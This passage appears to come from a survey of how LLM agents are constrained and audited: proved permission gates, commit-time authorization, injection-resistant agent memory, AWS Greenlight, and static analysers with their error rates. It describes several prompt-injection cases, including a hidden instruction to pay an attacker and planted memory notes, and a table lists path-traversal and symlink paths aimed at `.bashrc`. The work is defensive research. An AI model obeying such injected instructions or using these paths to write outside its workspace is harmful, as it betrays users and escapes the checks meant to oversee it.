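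The main theorem gives a condition under which an edited policy still allows every sequence of calls that the old policy allowed, however long. The condition requires a correspondence between the usage counters of the old and new permissions. Whenever the old policy could count a call against one of its permissions, the new policy must be able to count it against one of its own, and the counters must still correspond afterwards. Raising quotas or adding permissions at the end of the list always meets the condition. For many other edits, someone proposes a correspondence and Lean checks it.

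The researchers tested the check on 51 edits they wrote themselves. It certified all 21 that preserved the existing workflows and none of the 30 that broke one, so it raised no false alarms on this set. Edits by ordinary application developers might be messier. The check also certified a real quota increase from an open-source agent application.

An edit can pass this check and still be unsafe. For example, raising the quota for sending a report preserves every old workflow but also permits a second send. Safety needs separate rules, and the researchers took several attempts to get them right for the report example, where the agent must send the public fields of a private report to Alice once. A rule that the message must be classified as public lets the agent send Alice any public text. A second rule requires the message to come from `Sanitize`, the function that selects the approved fields,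 but the agent can still run `Sanitize` on an attacker's text and send the result. Only a third rule, that the input to `Sanitize` must come from reading the report, stops this, and it still allows all six legitimate orders of the steps. The gate enforced exactly the rules it had in each version, so none of its proofs would have revealed a missing rule.

Some of the gate's correct refusals would probably annoy a user. The harness cannot always determine whether a message went out, so a failed send uses up the quota and the gate blocks a retry. Each approval applies to one stored result, so if the agent recomputes a summary, the old approval doesn't cover the new one, even if the text is identical.

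### Approvals that no longer apply

A person's approval can also become outdated before the action takes effect. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, collected 17 security advisories about three agent products, all since fixed. In 12, the approval did not cover the action the product carried out. In the other five, the product still accepted the approval after the facts behind it had changed, such as when a script was rewritten.

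His remedy, commit-time authorization, is a check at the moment a service makes a change permanent. The service must then have one complete justification for exactly that change: an approval that is still in force, facts that still hold, finished prerequisites, an exact match between the approved action and the real one, and a workflow branch that nobody has cancelled.

A permission check must confirm that the facts behind an approval belong together. Suppose a person approves a change to a support ticket at version 7, and the ticket then moves to version 8. A second person approves the change at version 8 and later withdraws that approval. A gate that checks each fact separately can combine the first approval, which is still in force, with the version number from the second, and let the change through even though no current approval covers version 8. Santos-Grueiro proved in Lean that his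 check never accepts such a mixture. If a policy requires the facts behind an approval, every justification the check accepts contains an approval that is in force and was given for the current version. The proof assumes that the services issuing approvals and version numbers act honestly and never reuse an identifier.

The proof covers a model of the check, and experiments test the check with real software. In one experiment, agents based on three language models fixed bugs using OpenHands, an open-source coding agent, but their permission to publish to production was withdrawn before they published. A service that checked only the code version applied all 12 writes made after permission was withdrawn, while the protected service applied none. After 11 of 12 refusals that came without prior notice, the agents published to a test environment for which they had separate permission. The release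 instructions had named this alternative, so the experiment does not show what an agent would do without one.

The design limits needless blocks by accepting any one valid justification, even if others have expired. Some remain because the gate refuses the action whenever evidence is missing, for example during an outage at the approval service. Santos-Grueiro states that the guarantee does not cover such delays and refusals.

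### Agent memory

Many agents store notes that they reuse in later sessions, so an instruction hidden on a web page can enter the notes and cause harm weeks later. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) describes a memory system that trusts only what the user typed and what the user or a verifier model confirmed. For everything else, the agent's main model receives only references that hide the content, and a separate model without tools reads the untrusted notes.

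The two proved theorems are Action Integrity and Reasoning Integrity. Action Integrity means every argument that reaches a sensitive tool is either text the user typed or text the user confirmed, byte for byte, for that tool. Reasoning Integrity concerns two runs with the same user input and random choices but different untrusted notes. If the gate displays the same things and receives the same decisions in both runs, the agent takes the same actions and gives the same replies. Untrusted notes can therefore affect the agent's actions and replies only through what the gate displays.

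Lean has checked both theorems for a single user, but the results for memory shared between users have only written proofs. Jiang and colleagues also cite TMA-NM, a memory design whose author checked its safety with TLA+, a notation for modelling systems and searching their states.

A confirmation in this system covers a value and a tool, but not the task, the time or the other arguments. Once the user has confirmed `alice@example.org` for the email tool, the agent can later send Alice a different message without asking again. This reduces the number of prompts but may allow more than the user intended. The system also matches values by exact bytes, so if the user typed `alice@example.org` and the model writes `alice@Example.org`, the value goes to the gate for confirmation even though both addresses reach the same mailbox. On Trojan Hippo, a benchmark that plants dormant instructions in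 an agent's memory, the researchers recorded no successful attacks. As with *Agenra*, the person can still make the wrong decision at the gate.

### Skills and their declared capabilities

An agent skill is a set of written instructions for the model, often with scripts that the model can run. A manifest can list the capabilities that the skill needs, such as reading files or contacting the network. Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, defines capability containment as

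Π(τ) ⊆ D

where D is the declared list, τ is the record of a session, and Π(τ) is the set of capabilities that occur anywhere in that record.

Metere combines three methods. Abstract interpretation, the technique from the previous section, computes an upper bound on the effects of each script. A refinement type system, which attaches conditions to types of data, rejects any tool call whose capability is not in D. A solver then searches short sequences of calls for one whose actual effects differ from those the audit log lists as approved and executed. With 10 declared capabilities and 8 calls, it must cover 11⁸, or about 214 million, sequences. Metere argues that together these methods leave only one gap in his threat model, the LLM's freedom not to act, and that a check at the end of the session catches it.

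The argument is weakest on scripts. Metere assumes that existing analysers already produce the full set of effects for scripts in mainstream languages. CodeQL, one of the tools he names, did badly in the test by Cai and colleagues, which gives reason to doubt this. A sound analyser would also bring back the false alarms that solver-checked rules avoid.

Containment is also coarse. It compares kinds of capability, so a skill that declares file writing satisfies it whether it writes to `workspace/test/tests.py` or to `.bashrc`. A skill can also satisfy it by declaring every capability. Metere accepts this because an operator can see an overlong list and compare it with what the skill used. But the definition counts calls that the harness refused, so a hijacked model can break the property just by requesting a capability that the manifest leaves out.

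The four projects differ in how close their proofs come to the software that runs:

| Work | What the proof is about | What has to hold for the guarantee |
|---|---|---|
| *Agenra* | The Lean functions that check live calls | The Python layer translates correctly, tools do only what they declare, calls run one at a time |
| Santos-Grueiro | A Lean model of the check | Every protected action passes through the gate, the policy lists every relevant fact, the service checks and writes in one step |
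| Jiang and colleagues | A Lean model of the memory system for one user | The gate displays values faithfully, stored notes never change, labels reflect the true source |
| Metere | A written argument about three automatic checks | The script analyser misses nothing, the harness intercepts every tool call |

### Deriving rules from hazards

All of these proofs start from rules already written. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) proposes a procedure for finding those rules. It adapts System-Theoretic Process Analysis, a method aviation engineers use to trace accidents to interactions between parts that each work as intended.

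One example is a calendar agent that can list events, change events and send email. A user books an appointment to treat a sexually transmitted disease, and it clashes with a meeting with a colleague, Bob. The agent moves the meeting and emails Bob, giving the reason in the subject line. Each tool worked correctly, and no attacker was involved.

The analysis lists the people whom the agent affects, here the user and the other attendees, and what each of them values, such as privacy and timely notice. It turns each value into a possible loss, looks for behaviour that could cause the loss, and selects the losses that matter enough to prevent. The results are requirements in English, which the researchers then restate as rules that a gate can enforce:

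| Requirement | Rule |
|---|---|
| Notification emails contain only essential event details, and no private information unless the user authorises it | Event details are private to non-attendees, anything derived from private information is at least as private, and no email contains data that is private to its recipient |
| The agent promptly tells attendees about any change | One email to every attendee directly follows each change to an event |

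The first rule restricts where data may flow, and the second restricts the order of tool calls. For enforcement, the researchers sort actions into four groups: those the gate always blocks, those it requires, those it allows without asking, and those that need the user's confirmation.

To apply the data-flow rule, the gate needs a way to identify private data. Doshi and colleagues propose extending the Model Context Protocol to require tool servers to attach labels for capabilities, confidentiality and trustworthiness. If a label is "unsure", the gate asks the user. A wrong label from a tool server would make the rule ineffective, so they suggest that companies restrict agents to tools from vendors they trust.

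They tested the idea on a model of the extended protocol in Alloy, a modelling language whose analyser searches all runs up to a fixed length. Without the rules, the analyser quickly found runs that leaked private data. With the rules it found none, while useful runs remained possible, such as rescheduling an event and notifying the participants. Keeping useful runs possible matters as much as preventing leaks, because a rule that stopped all email would also prevent every leak. The check does not cover longer runs or the behaviour of a real agent.

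The rules can still block harmless messages. An email telling Bob only that the user has a clash at noon uses information from a private event, so the data-flow rule blocks it until the user confirms. The researchers also mention a stricter variant that would block all email after the agent has listed the user's events. That variant conflicts with the rule that the agent must notify attendees of any change, because the agent has to list events to find clashes in the first place. A solver can detect this kind of conflict once both rules are written as formulas, as in AWS's Gold refund example, but it cannot choose which rule to relax.

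### AWS Greenlight

AWS extended this approach at its re:Invent conference in December 2026 with Greenlight, a service available in preview. According to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules*, Greenlight denies an agent all tools and network destinations by default, and the customer decides which to open. A language model drafts rules from the customer's procedures, security standards and logs of past tool calls. Automated reasoning then flags conflicting rules and looks for ways to reach resources outside the agent's approved access. Either AgentCore Gateway or a sandbox called Strands Box enforces the rules outside the harness, so the agent can't change them.

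AWS presents the service as a way to let agents work with less supervision. Companies have kept people approving the steps they wanted to automate. Expansión's *Limitar los agentes de IA los haría inservibles* (2026) reports that AWS's marketing chief, Julia White, attributes this to uncertainty about how agents will behave. According to the article, tight limits make agents less useful, but under loose limits they may act in unexpected ways.

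AWS's executives have described the guarantee differently, and the logic supports Shawn Bice's narrower version. Chief executive Matt Garman said in his keynote that the logic proves there is no way for an agent to break a specified rule, as reported in ITWeb's *AWS creates gateway to ‘trust’ AI agents*. In Computertrends' *AWS Greenlight staví matematické zábrany kolem agentů s umělou inteligencí*, Bice limits the proof to the policies and the system that the customer has specified and modelled, and calls Greenlight one tool among several.

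Garman also argued from success rates. An agent that makes an error in 0.1% of its steps gets through 1,000 steps without an error only about 35% of the time. A gate can stop the errors that break a rule, but a blocked call still needs a retry, another route or a person, and errors within the rules remain. Checking rules can make an agent's failures less harmful without helping it finish more tasks.

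Greenlight's most useful feature for reducing false alarms is probably its preview, which shows a team which recorded tool calls and scenarios a proposed rule would block. If the list includes harmless calls, the team can correct the rule before accepting it. The recorded calls cover only what agents have already done, so the rule could still block a new kind of legitimate task.

### Whether a decidable rule language ends the trade-off

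In a language like Cedar, a solver can settle questions about any rule, which removes one source of false alarms. If the analysis reports that a policy allows a request, the policy does allow it. The analysers in the previous section, by contrast, could report behaviour that no run would produce.

The blocks and missed violations at run time come from the rules themselves. The two versions of the `write_file` rule from the start of this section show how they persist after a correct proof:

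| Path in the tool call | Real location | Rule: starts with `workspace/` | Same rule, and no `..` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `workspace/test/tests.py` | inside | allows | allows |
| `workspace/notes..txt` | inside | allows | blocks a harmless write |
| `workspace/../.bashrc` | outside | allows a violation | blocks |
| `workspace/shared/.bashrc`, where `shared` is a link to the home folder | outside | allows a violation | allows a violation |

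The solver proved the second version correct, but that version still allows a path it should block and blocks a path it should allow. Refusing `..` only where it is a complete step in the path would allow `workspace/notes..txt`, but would still block `workspace/test/../notes.txt`, which resolves to a file inside the workspace. Applying the rule to the resolved path, as the formula in the first section does, gives the right answer in all four rows. However, the formula then doesn't cover the code that resolves the path, and another process can redirect a link between the check and the write. Santos-Grueiro lists redirected links among the changes that can invalidate an approval, and proposes repeating the check in the same step as the write.

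Even a rule that gets all four rows right can block something the user wants, such as the change to `.bashrc` that a developer requested in the test by Adam and colleagues. An exception for approved writes would solve this but would require an approval prompt.

Translating rules from English is another source of errors, and it grows as language models draft more of the rules. AgentCore lets administrators describe a policy in ordinary language, which a model then turns into Cedar. The system checks that the result refers to real tools and arguments, and AWS uses the solver to find policies that allow everything, allow nothing or contain impossible conditions. Suppose an administrator wants discounts for orders of at least 50 items and the model writes 500. The policy passes all of these checks because it refers to a real argument and allows some orders but not others, yet it wrongly refuses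 the discount for orders of 50 to 499 items. AWS acknowledges in *Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails add new policy refinement workflows* (2026), which concerns a related product that checks a model's written answers, that the quality of the results depends on how well the customer has defined the policy.

Most of the requirements in this section describe calls that the gate must refuse, but a solver can also find needless blocks if a developer states, in the same notation, which calls the gate must allow. For the `write_file` rule, one such requirement is that the gate accepts every path made of `workspace/` followed by a file name without a slash, unless that name is exactly `..`. The solver would return a counterexample such as `workspace/notes..txt`, so the developer would learn of the false alarm before any user did.

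## Static analysers tested on real agent projects

Static analysers of whole agent projects cannot give the exact answers that solvers give about permission rules. Researchers have run these analysers on thousands of open-source agent projects and on collections of known bugs, and counted how many of the analysers' reports were correct. Fewer researchers have counted how many bugs the analysers missed.

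### Recovering an agent from framework code

Wang and colleagues show how their analyser, AgentFlow, handles the research agent mentioned earlier, which can hand its work to an operations agent with an email tool. The developer creates the operations agent with `Agent(name="OpsAgent", tools=[send_email])` and lists it under `handoffs` when creating the research agent. A general analyser finds only that each line creates an object and stores a list in it, because the framework makes the tool call and the handoff while the agent runs.

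AgentFlow first recognises the constructs that have a special meaning in a framework, such as the `Agent` constructor. It then traces each name back to its definition, so that `send_email` in the tool list leads to the object that holds the email tool's settings. Finally, it translates what it found into short facts that look the same for every framework:

| In the code | Fact |
|---|---|
| `tools=[send_email]` | Call(OpsAgent, SendEmail) |
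| `handoffs=[handoff(agent=ops_agent)]` | Transfer(ResearchAgent, OpsAgent) |
| `require_approval: "always"` on the email tool | BranchIf(ApprovalPolicy, SendEmail) |
| `session=session` when the run starts | WriteState(ResearchAgent, ResearchMem) |

These facts become the nodes and edges of a graph. Across 60 sampled projects, AgentFlow recovered a median of 17 nodes and 28 edges, while Agent-Wiz, a tool that parses the code without tracing names, recovered 4 nodes and no edges. The counts measure how much structure each tool extracts, and a larger graph can still contain wrong edges.

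APSIS, an analyser by Chen, Li and colleagues described in *Automated Safety Analysis for Agentic Workflows* (2026), reads the graph that an agent framework builds from a developer's code, without running the workflow. In LangGraph, for example, a developer connects two steps with a call such as `add_edge("save", "end")`, and the two names are only text until the framework stores them in its graph. Because APSIS reads the finished graph, it gets the right connections even if the code adds them in a loop, which an analyser of the source text would have to work out. If an edge's destination remains unknown until the agent runs, APSIS assumes that the edge is unsafe, which avoids some missed bugs but causes some false alarms.

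### Bugs in the wiring of a workflow

Chen and colleagues collected 861 issue reports about 13 frameworks and classified 783 of them as workflow bugs, meaning defects in how a developer connected the steps. About a quarter can be seen from the nodes and edges alone. For example, an `analyze` step passes its result to a `verify` step, which always passes it back. The researchers cite an incident in which a runaway loop between agents cost $47,000 before anyone noticed.

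The other three quarters depend on how the framework treats a step. For example, two parallel steps may write to the same channel, a named slot of shared data, and one value can overwrite the other if the developer has not declared how to merge them. The merge rule does not change the graph's nodes or edges, so a tool like Agentproof, which checks a plain workflow graph, could not detect that the rule is missing. APSIS adds the channels and their merge rules to the graph, along with labels for details such as which inputs a step must receive.

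It then searches the graph for twelve patterns. The pattern for the overwritten value is, in simplified notation,

report(c) ⇐ keepsLast(c) ∧ writes(u, c) ∧ writes(v, c) ∧ concurrent(u, v)

where c is a channel that keeps only the last value, and u and v are steps. The paper defines two different steps as concurrent if neither can reach the other in the graph. Taken literally, this definition also covers two steps on alternative branches. Suppose a router sends each run to either `save` or `write_home`, and both steps write to a channel called `status`. Neither step can reach the other, so the pattern matches, but no run executes both and nothing is lost. As in the five-node workflow in an earlier section, the graph lacks the information that would rule the problem out.

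To test APSIS, the researchers selected 135 bug reports that each had a reproducible workflow and a fix the maintainers had accepted. An ideal analyser would report every buggy workflow and none of the fixed ones. APSIS had a recall of 0.84, a precision of 0.91 and a false-positive rate of 0.08. The rates for the individual frameworks imply that it caught 113 of the 135 bugs and flagged 11 of the 135 fixed workflows.

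The false alarm rate was 3% for LangGraph and 17% for Flowise, a visual builder. By type of bug, it was zero for data of the wrong type and 20% for misrouted steps. Chen and colleagues do not explain the 11 cases individually, but one of the routing patterns may be a cause. It reports any step that a router can reach under two different labels, and a developer may have good reason to send both "urgent" and "normal" requests to the same step.

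They ran several other methods on the same 270 workflows:

| Method | Precision | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| The frameworks' own validators | none reported | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| CodeQL | 0.71 | 0.07 | 0.03 |
| CodeQL with an added graph reader | 0.74 | 0.17 | 0.06 |
| GPT-5.5 as judge | 0.60 | 0.80 | 0.54 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 as judge | 0.61 | 0.77 | 0.49 |
| DeepSeek-V4 as judge | 0.57 | 0.88 | 0.67 |
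| APSIS | 0.91 | 0.84 | 0.08 |

CodeQL, a general analyser that also did badly on the attacks Cai and colleagues collected, finds calls such as `add_edge` but not the workflow they build. Its standard queries do not apply to workflows that visual builders export as data files. The researchers wrote an extension that reads the graph directly, but recall rose to only 0.17 because most of the bugs depend on details such as merge rules and required inputs.

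The language models received the source code of one workflow at a time and a list of the six bug categories. They found most of the buggy workflows but also flagged about half or more of the fixed ones. Many of their correct verdicts were probably luck, since recall fell to between 0.39 and 0.44 when the models also had to name the right category. The prompt asked for a separate verdict on each category, so a model had six chances to raise a false alarm on each workflow. Newer models may do better.

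APSIS's recall fell from 0.84 to 0.50 without the patterns that use the behavioural labels. This comparison covers recall only, so it does not show how many of the 11 false alarms those patterns caused.

Chen and colleagues also ran APSIS on more than 40 actively maintained projects and found 36 previously unreported bugs. Maintainers fixed 33 of them and confirmed the other three. One was in an example that ships with NVIDIA's NeMo Agent Toolkit, where parallel steps write summaries of a batch to one channel without a merge rule. The example works on small batches but can fail or lose a summary on larger ones. Confirmation by maintainers is stronger evidence than a researcher's own reading of the code, but APSIS's precision on live projects can't be calculated without the number of false alarms.

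### Loops without a limit

An agent repeats model calls and tool calls by design, so an analyser that reported every loop would flag every agent. IAL-Scan, the analyser in *When Agents Do Not Stop*, is meant to report only loops that nothing reliably stops. One such loop, in the open-source project bisheng, calls the model again as long as its output includes a web search request, and adds each exchange to the conversation. IAL-Scan records that the loop ends when the requests stop, but does not count this exit as a limit because it depends on the model's output.

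IAL-Scan works in four steps. It first extracts facts from the source code, such as loops, model calls, growing message lists and turn limits, and adds the links that each framework creates implicitly. It then combines them into a graph and looks for groups of nodes that can all reach one another (strongly connected components). For each group, it checks whether the repetition reaches a costly call or makes stored data grow, and whether a limit covers the whole repeated path. For example, a turn limit on an inner agent does not stop an outer loop that keeps restarting that agent. Finally, a language model examines the code around each ambiguous candidate. The model can only propose dropping a candidate, and IAL-Scan accepts the proposal only if the code supports the stated reason.

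The researchers ran IAL-Scan on 6,549 Python repositories that use eight agent frameworks. The static steps produced 340 candidates in 264 projects, and the model, GPT-5.5, reduced them to 74. After reading the code, the researchers confirmed 68 of the 74, in 47 projects, a precision of 91.9%. The most common patterns were uncapped retries, uncapped repeated tool calls, and conversations between agents with no turn limit. "Confirmed" means the code has a repeated path with no strong limit, though the agent may never have looped for long.

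Most of that precision comes from the model. Without it, 68 of 340 reports would be correct, or 20%. This figure counts every candidate the model dropped as a false alarm, though some of those were probably real failures. When the researchers repeated the model's step twice on the same 340 candidates, it kept 64 and then 60 of the 68 confirmed failures. Three other language models kept between 41 and 54.

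In all six false alarms, IAL-Scan correctly traced the path of a real loop but overlooked its limit. One agent relied on the framework's default of three iterations, another loop had a cap of two tool calls, and two workflows kept a counter outside the loop body. Another workflow combined a retry budget with timeouts, and the last case was a conversation that always ended after two turns. IAL-Scan's framework models prevent many more false alarms. With them switched off, the number of reports rose from 74 to 276, of which 215 were false.

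The researchers looked for missed failures only in the 264 projects that had candidates, not in the other 6,285, where the static steps had found nothing, so they did not measure recall over the whole corpus. They used two methods based on language models, the coding agent Codex and direct prompting one file at a time. These flagged 239 places that IAL-Scan had not reported, and 7 of them were real failures. Together with the 68 failures IAL-Scan found, this means the 264 projects contain at least 75, so IAL-Scan's recall on them is at most 91%.

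The paper's comparison of the three methods needs the same caution, because all 68 confirmed failures came from IAL-Scan's own reports. IAL-Scan therefore could not have missed any of them, while Codex found 50 and direct prompting found 23.

### Text that reaches a dangerous tool

Other analysers look for paths along which untrusted text could reach a powerful operation, such as running a command. TaintP2X traces text generated by a language model to such operations, in applications whose ordinary code calls the model. According to Wang and colleagues, it does not analyse programs written with agent frameworks, so it does not cover handoffs and tool lists like those in the email example.

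AgentFlow does cover them. It reports a prompt p, an agent a and a sensitive tool c if three conditions hold:

- text from p can reach a, directly or through other agents and shared memory;
- a can start c, possibly by way of other agents;
- text from a can enter the arguments of c.

The 238 projects it flagged contained 4,357 such combinations, and in 129 of the projects the tool could send data to an outside service. Of 100 sampled reports, 73 were correct, and most of the false ones came from coarse descriptions of what a tool can do.

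AgentFlow's graph contains the rule that a person must approve every email, but the three conditions ignore it. The path from the operations agent to the email tool runs through the approval policy, which the query treats like any other node. Taken literally, the query therefore reports an email tool that always asks for approval first. Whether this is a false alarm depends on whether the reader trusts the approval prompt or expects users to click through it.

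AgentSecGraph, the analyser in *Beyond Predefined Sinks*, records such protections explicitly. The paper shows why this is needed with three tools that run a shell command. The first runs whatever the agent supplies, the second replaces the agent's text with a fixed command, and the third checks the text against a list of allowed commands. A search for command execution would report all three.

AgentSecGraph found 23,866 sensitive operations in 67 repositories. It found evidence that outside text could influence 41% of them and signs of a protective check around 13%. The paper treats these operations as starting points for review and counts none as a vulnerability without further evidence. It reports no precision or recall. The researcher also reproduced 22 sensitive behaviours in 13 repositories. One was a confirmed vulnerability and one still awaited disclosure. The other 20 did not count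 as vulnerabilities because of existing protections or the conditions of use. The 22 cases are not a random sample, so 1 in 22 is not an estimate of precision, but they suggest that existing protections would be the main source of false alarms if someone treated every operation as a bug.

*Agent Audit* (Zhang and Nian, 2026) describes a scanner for Python agents that combines data tracing with searches for exposed passwords, risky configuration files and excessive privileges. The scanner found 40 of the 42 known vulnerabilities in 22 samples and raised 6 false alarms, a precision of 87% and a recall of 95%.

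*AgentLens* (2026), which presents a competing auditing tool, reports, however, that Agent Audit identified no validated vulnerabilities in Langflow, a large and popular visual builder for agents. It attributes such failures to static tools being unable to determine whether the model would ever choose the vulnerable tool and whether a run-time check would block the call. One project tested by a competitor is thin evidence, but a set of 22 samples with 42 known vulnerabilities is much denser in bugs than most code, which favours a scanner's precision.

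### Flaws in the harness itself

AgentFlow and IAL-Scan rely on knowledge of particular frameworks, which does not help with agents that run their own loops. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents ClawAudit, which searches the source code of one such agent, OpenClaw, for security flaws. The researchers split 446 published security advisories about OpenClaw by date. They wrote rules from the 229 older ones and tested them once on the 217 newer ones, which they collected only after finishing the rules.

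General tools found few of the newer flaws. Semgrep, which searches code for patterns, found 21.7% with about 2,815 standard rules, and CodeQL found 13.8%. The researchers say these rules target operations typical of web applications, whereas an agent builds prompts, loads skills and writes to memory through its own functions. After they added 47 rules to Semgrep and 30 queries to CodeQL, Semgrep found 66.8% and CodeQL found 75.1%. The gain was especially large for flaws in which a file-system link redirects a write, as with the `workspace/shared` folder in the previous section. Semgrep's standard rules found none of the 15 such flaws in the full set of advisories, and the extended rules found 13.

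The scoring method probably inflates these shares because it counts a flaw as found if the tool reports anything in a file that the fix later changed, even an unrelated problem. A rule that flagged every file would score 100%. Zhang and colleagues chose this method because fixes often move code, so line numbers rarely match, and they acknowledge that it can overcount successes.

They also ran the rules on the current version of OpenClaw, which has 16,433 files, and checked 25 reports from each tool by hand. For each tool, three of the 25 were real, a precision of 12%. At least some of the false alarms occur because many rules report a risky operation if the surrounding code contains no protective check, but developers often put such checks in a separate helper function. The Semgrep version looks only at the immediately surrounding code. The CodeQL version also recognises calls to helpers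 within the same function, but it still reports safe code if a different function did the checking earlier.

The 75% comes from snapshots that each contained a known flaw, while the 12% comes from scanning a whole program after its maintainers had fixed hundreds of reported flaws. By then, few of the places that matched a rule were still dangerous.

### Precision when bugs are rare

The APSIS benchmark also contains many more bugs than ordinary code probably does, since exactly half of its workflows are buggy. If r is the recall, f the false-positive rate and π the share of workflows that have a bug, then

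precision = r·π / (r·π + f·(1 − π))

With APSIS's r = 0.84 and f = 0.08, a benchmark with π = 0.5 gives 0.42 / (0.42 + 0.04), or about 0.91, which matches the published figure. Now suppose that only 5% of workflows have a bug. Out of 1,000 workflows, 50 are buggy and APSIS reports 42 of them. It also reports 8% of the 950 correct workflows, which is 76. Only 42 of the 118 reports are then real, a precision of about 0.36. The table gives the same calculation for other shares, and for GPT-5.5 as a judge:

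| Share of workflows with a bug | Precision of APSIS | Precision of GPT-5.5 |
|---|---|---|
| 50% | 0.91 | 0.60 |
| 20% | 0.72 | 0.27 |
| 10% | 0.54 | 0.14 |
| 5% | 0.36 | 0.07 |
| 1% | 0.10 | 0.01 |

If 5% of workflows were buggy, APSIS would need a false-positive rate of about 0.5%, one sixteenth of the measured rate, to keep a precision of 0.9. If only 1% were buggy, the rate would have to be even lower.

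Nobody has measured the real share. APSIS found confirmed bugs in 21 of somewhat more than 40 repositories, which suggests that projects commonly have at least one. But a project can contain many workflows, most of them correct, and the projects studied may not be typical. IAL-Scan looked for one kind of bug and confirmed it in 47 of 6,549 projects, or 0.7%. The bottom rows of the table are probably the relevant ones for such a tool.

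Eleven false alarms among 135 workflows are compatible with a true false-positive rate of about 5% to 14%. If 5% of workflows have a bug, precision could therefore be anywhere from about a quarter to a half.

The fixed workflows may also differ from ordinary correct ones, so the false-alarm rate on ordinary workflows could be lower or higher than 8%. A fixed workflow may differ from its buggy version by a single edge or setting, so it resembles a bug more closely than most correct workflows do. If APSIS tends to flag such near misses, its rate on ordinary workflows would be lower. But the researchers kept only bugs that they could reproduce with a minimal workflow. A production workflow with dozens of steps and several routers has many more places where one of the twelve patterns could match by accident, which could raise the rate. Running APSIS on a random sample of working projects and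 checking every report would settle the question.

The benchmark may also overstate APSIS's performance. Chen and colleagues derived their bug categories from 31 of the collected reports and drew the 135 test pairs from the same collection, so some of those 31 reports may also be in the test set. The test of ClawAudit avoided this problem by using only advisories newer than the rules.

### Missed bugs

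Precision is calculated from the reports alone, so a bug that an analyser misses has no effect on it. An analyser that reported only the single most obvious bug in 6,549 projects would have a precision of 100%. Some evidence about missed bugs exists for five of the seven analysers:

| Analyser | Correct reports | Missed bugs that the researchers found |
|---|---|---|
| APSIS | 113 of 124 | 22 of 135 known bugs |
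| IAL-Scan | 68 of 74 | 7, in the 264 projects with candidates |
| AgentFlow | 73 of 100 sampled | 9, in 100 unreported agents with powerful tools |
| Agent Audit | 40 of 46 | 2 of 42 known vulnerabilities |
| ClawAudit with CodeQL | 3 of 25 sampled | 54 of 217 known flaws |

An analyser that misses even one bug of a given type is not sound for that type, so none of these five is sound. AgentSecGraph isn't sound either, as its paper states, because it follows data only locally and can lose track of tools that a program registers while it runs. The ClawAudit row also shows that an analyser can raise many false alarms and still miss a quarter of the flaws.

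High precision can come at the expense of soundness. IAL-Scan discards loops that look like parsers, tests or routine polling, and lets a language model remove more. If it cannot determine where a call leads, it records the gap but adds no edge to the graph, so it may miss an infinite loop that passes through that call. APSIS instead treats unknown edges as unsafe. IAL-Scan's choices are sensible for a tool that developers use voluntarily, since they stop reading reports when too many are wrong, as a later section shows. Someone who has to certify that an agent always stops would need to put soundness ahead of precision.

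In the example with 1,000 workflows and 50 bugs, APSIS reports nothing for 8 buggy workflows and 874 correct ones. A workflow without a report therefore has about a 0.9% chance of containing a bug, compared with 5% before the analysis. If half of all workflows were buggy, the figure would be about 15%. Both estimates cover only bugs that leave a trace in the graph, because Chen and colleagues included no others in the benchmark. IAL-Scan's definition similarly leaves out agents that stay within their limits but make no progress, if the lack of progress shows only in the meaning of their messages.

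## Checks on single tool calls in benchmark experiments

A permission gate judges a single call after the model requests it and before it takes effect, whereas a static analyser has to allow for every call the model might request. The gate can use the call's actual arguments and facts that did not exist at deployment, such as what earlier tools returned, what the user has typed, which programs are installed on the machine and what a file contains now.

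This extra knowledge removes the false alarms that come from unknown values and impossible paths. In the five-node workflow, a person has already approved the change in every run that reaches `write_home`, so a gate there would never raise the alarm that the graph search raised. A gate still raises false alarms when its rule is too strict or when it lacks a fact it needs. Researchers measure how much a gate hinders an agent by running the same agent on the same tasks with and without it.

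### AgentDojo

AgentDojo, a benchmark from 2024, tests agents against prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in material that the agent reads. It has four suites: banking, travel, messaging in Slack, and a workspace of email, calendar and files. Each suite pairs every user task with every attacker goal, so banking, with 16 tasks and 9 goals, has 144 pairs. In one pair, the user asks the agent to pay a bill, and the file with the bill also contains an instruction to send money to the attacker's account first.

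The benchmark's two main measures are utility and attack success rate. Utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes, called benign utility when no attack is present. The attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker reaches the goal. Both measures are necessary because guardrails that restrict an agent may also reduce its ability to complete tasks, a concern that *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (2026) raises.

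Needless blocks can lower benign utility, but the drop measures them only indirectly, because an agent may complete the task by another route after a block or fail it for reasons unrelated to the gate. The attack success rate can also mislead. In one experiment, AgentDojo counted 11 of 105 Slack attacks as successful although the gate had blocked every malicious call in them. For the attacker's goal in these cases, the benchmark checks the calls the agent requested, whether or not they ran.

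### Drafting rules from a written policy

Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, describe a system that turns an organisation's written policy into rules for a gate. It works in four steps:

1. Ordinary code splits the policy into clauses.
2. A language model drafts rules for each clause. It can only complete the phrase "block when", using a condition from a fixed list that a person prepared, and name the tools that the rule covers. The system repeats this step five times.
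3. Code checks each draft against the tool schemas, which list every tool's name and arguments. It also uses two tables, which show which tools can lift each condition and which arguments each condition examines. Drafts that most of the five rounds did not produce drop out.
4. Code saves the remaining rules, each with the policy sentence behind it.

When the agent runs, the gate evaluates these rules without a language model, in about 3 microseconds per call. It takes facts only from tool results and the user's own messages, so the model's claim that the user has approved a payment has no effect. If the gate blocks a call, it returns an error with the name of the rule, and the agent can change its plan.

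A rule can be a prohibition, which blocks a call while its condition holds, or a precondition, which blocks a call until its condition holds. If the gate lacks the fact it needs to check the condition, a prohibition lets the call through, which can cause a missed violation, and a precondition blocks it, which can cause a false alarm.

Yu and colleagues compiled the airline and retail policies of τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service. The checks in step 3 repaired or rejected 29 of the 79 airline drafts and 7 of the 53 retail drafts:

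| Defect in the drafted rule | Airline | Retail |
|---|---|---|
| Covers every tool, and the code cannot narrow it to particular ones | 11 | 2 |
| Examines an argument that the tool does not have | 8 | 1 |
| Waits for something that no tool in the domain can bring about | 5 | 0 |
| Demands the customer's confirmation before calls that only read data | 5 | 0 |
| Blocks the very tools that would lift the block | 0 | 4 |
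| Total | 29 of 79 | 7 of 53 |

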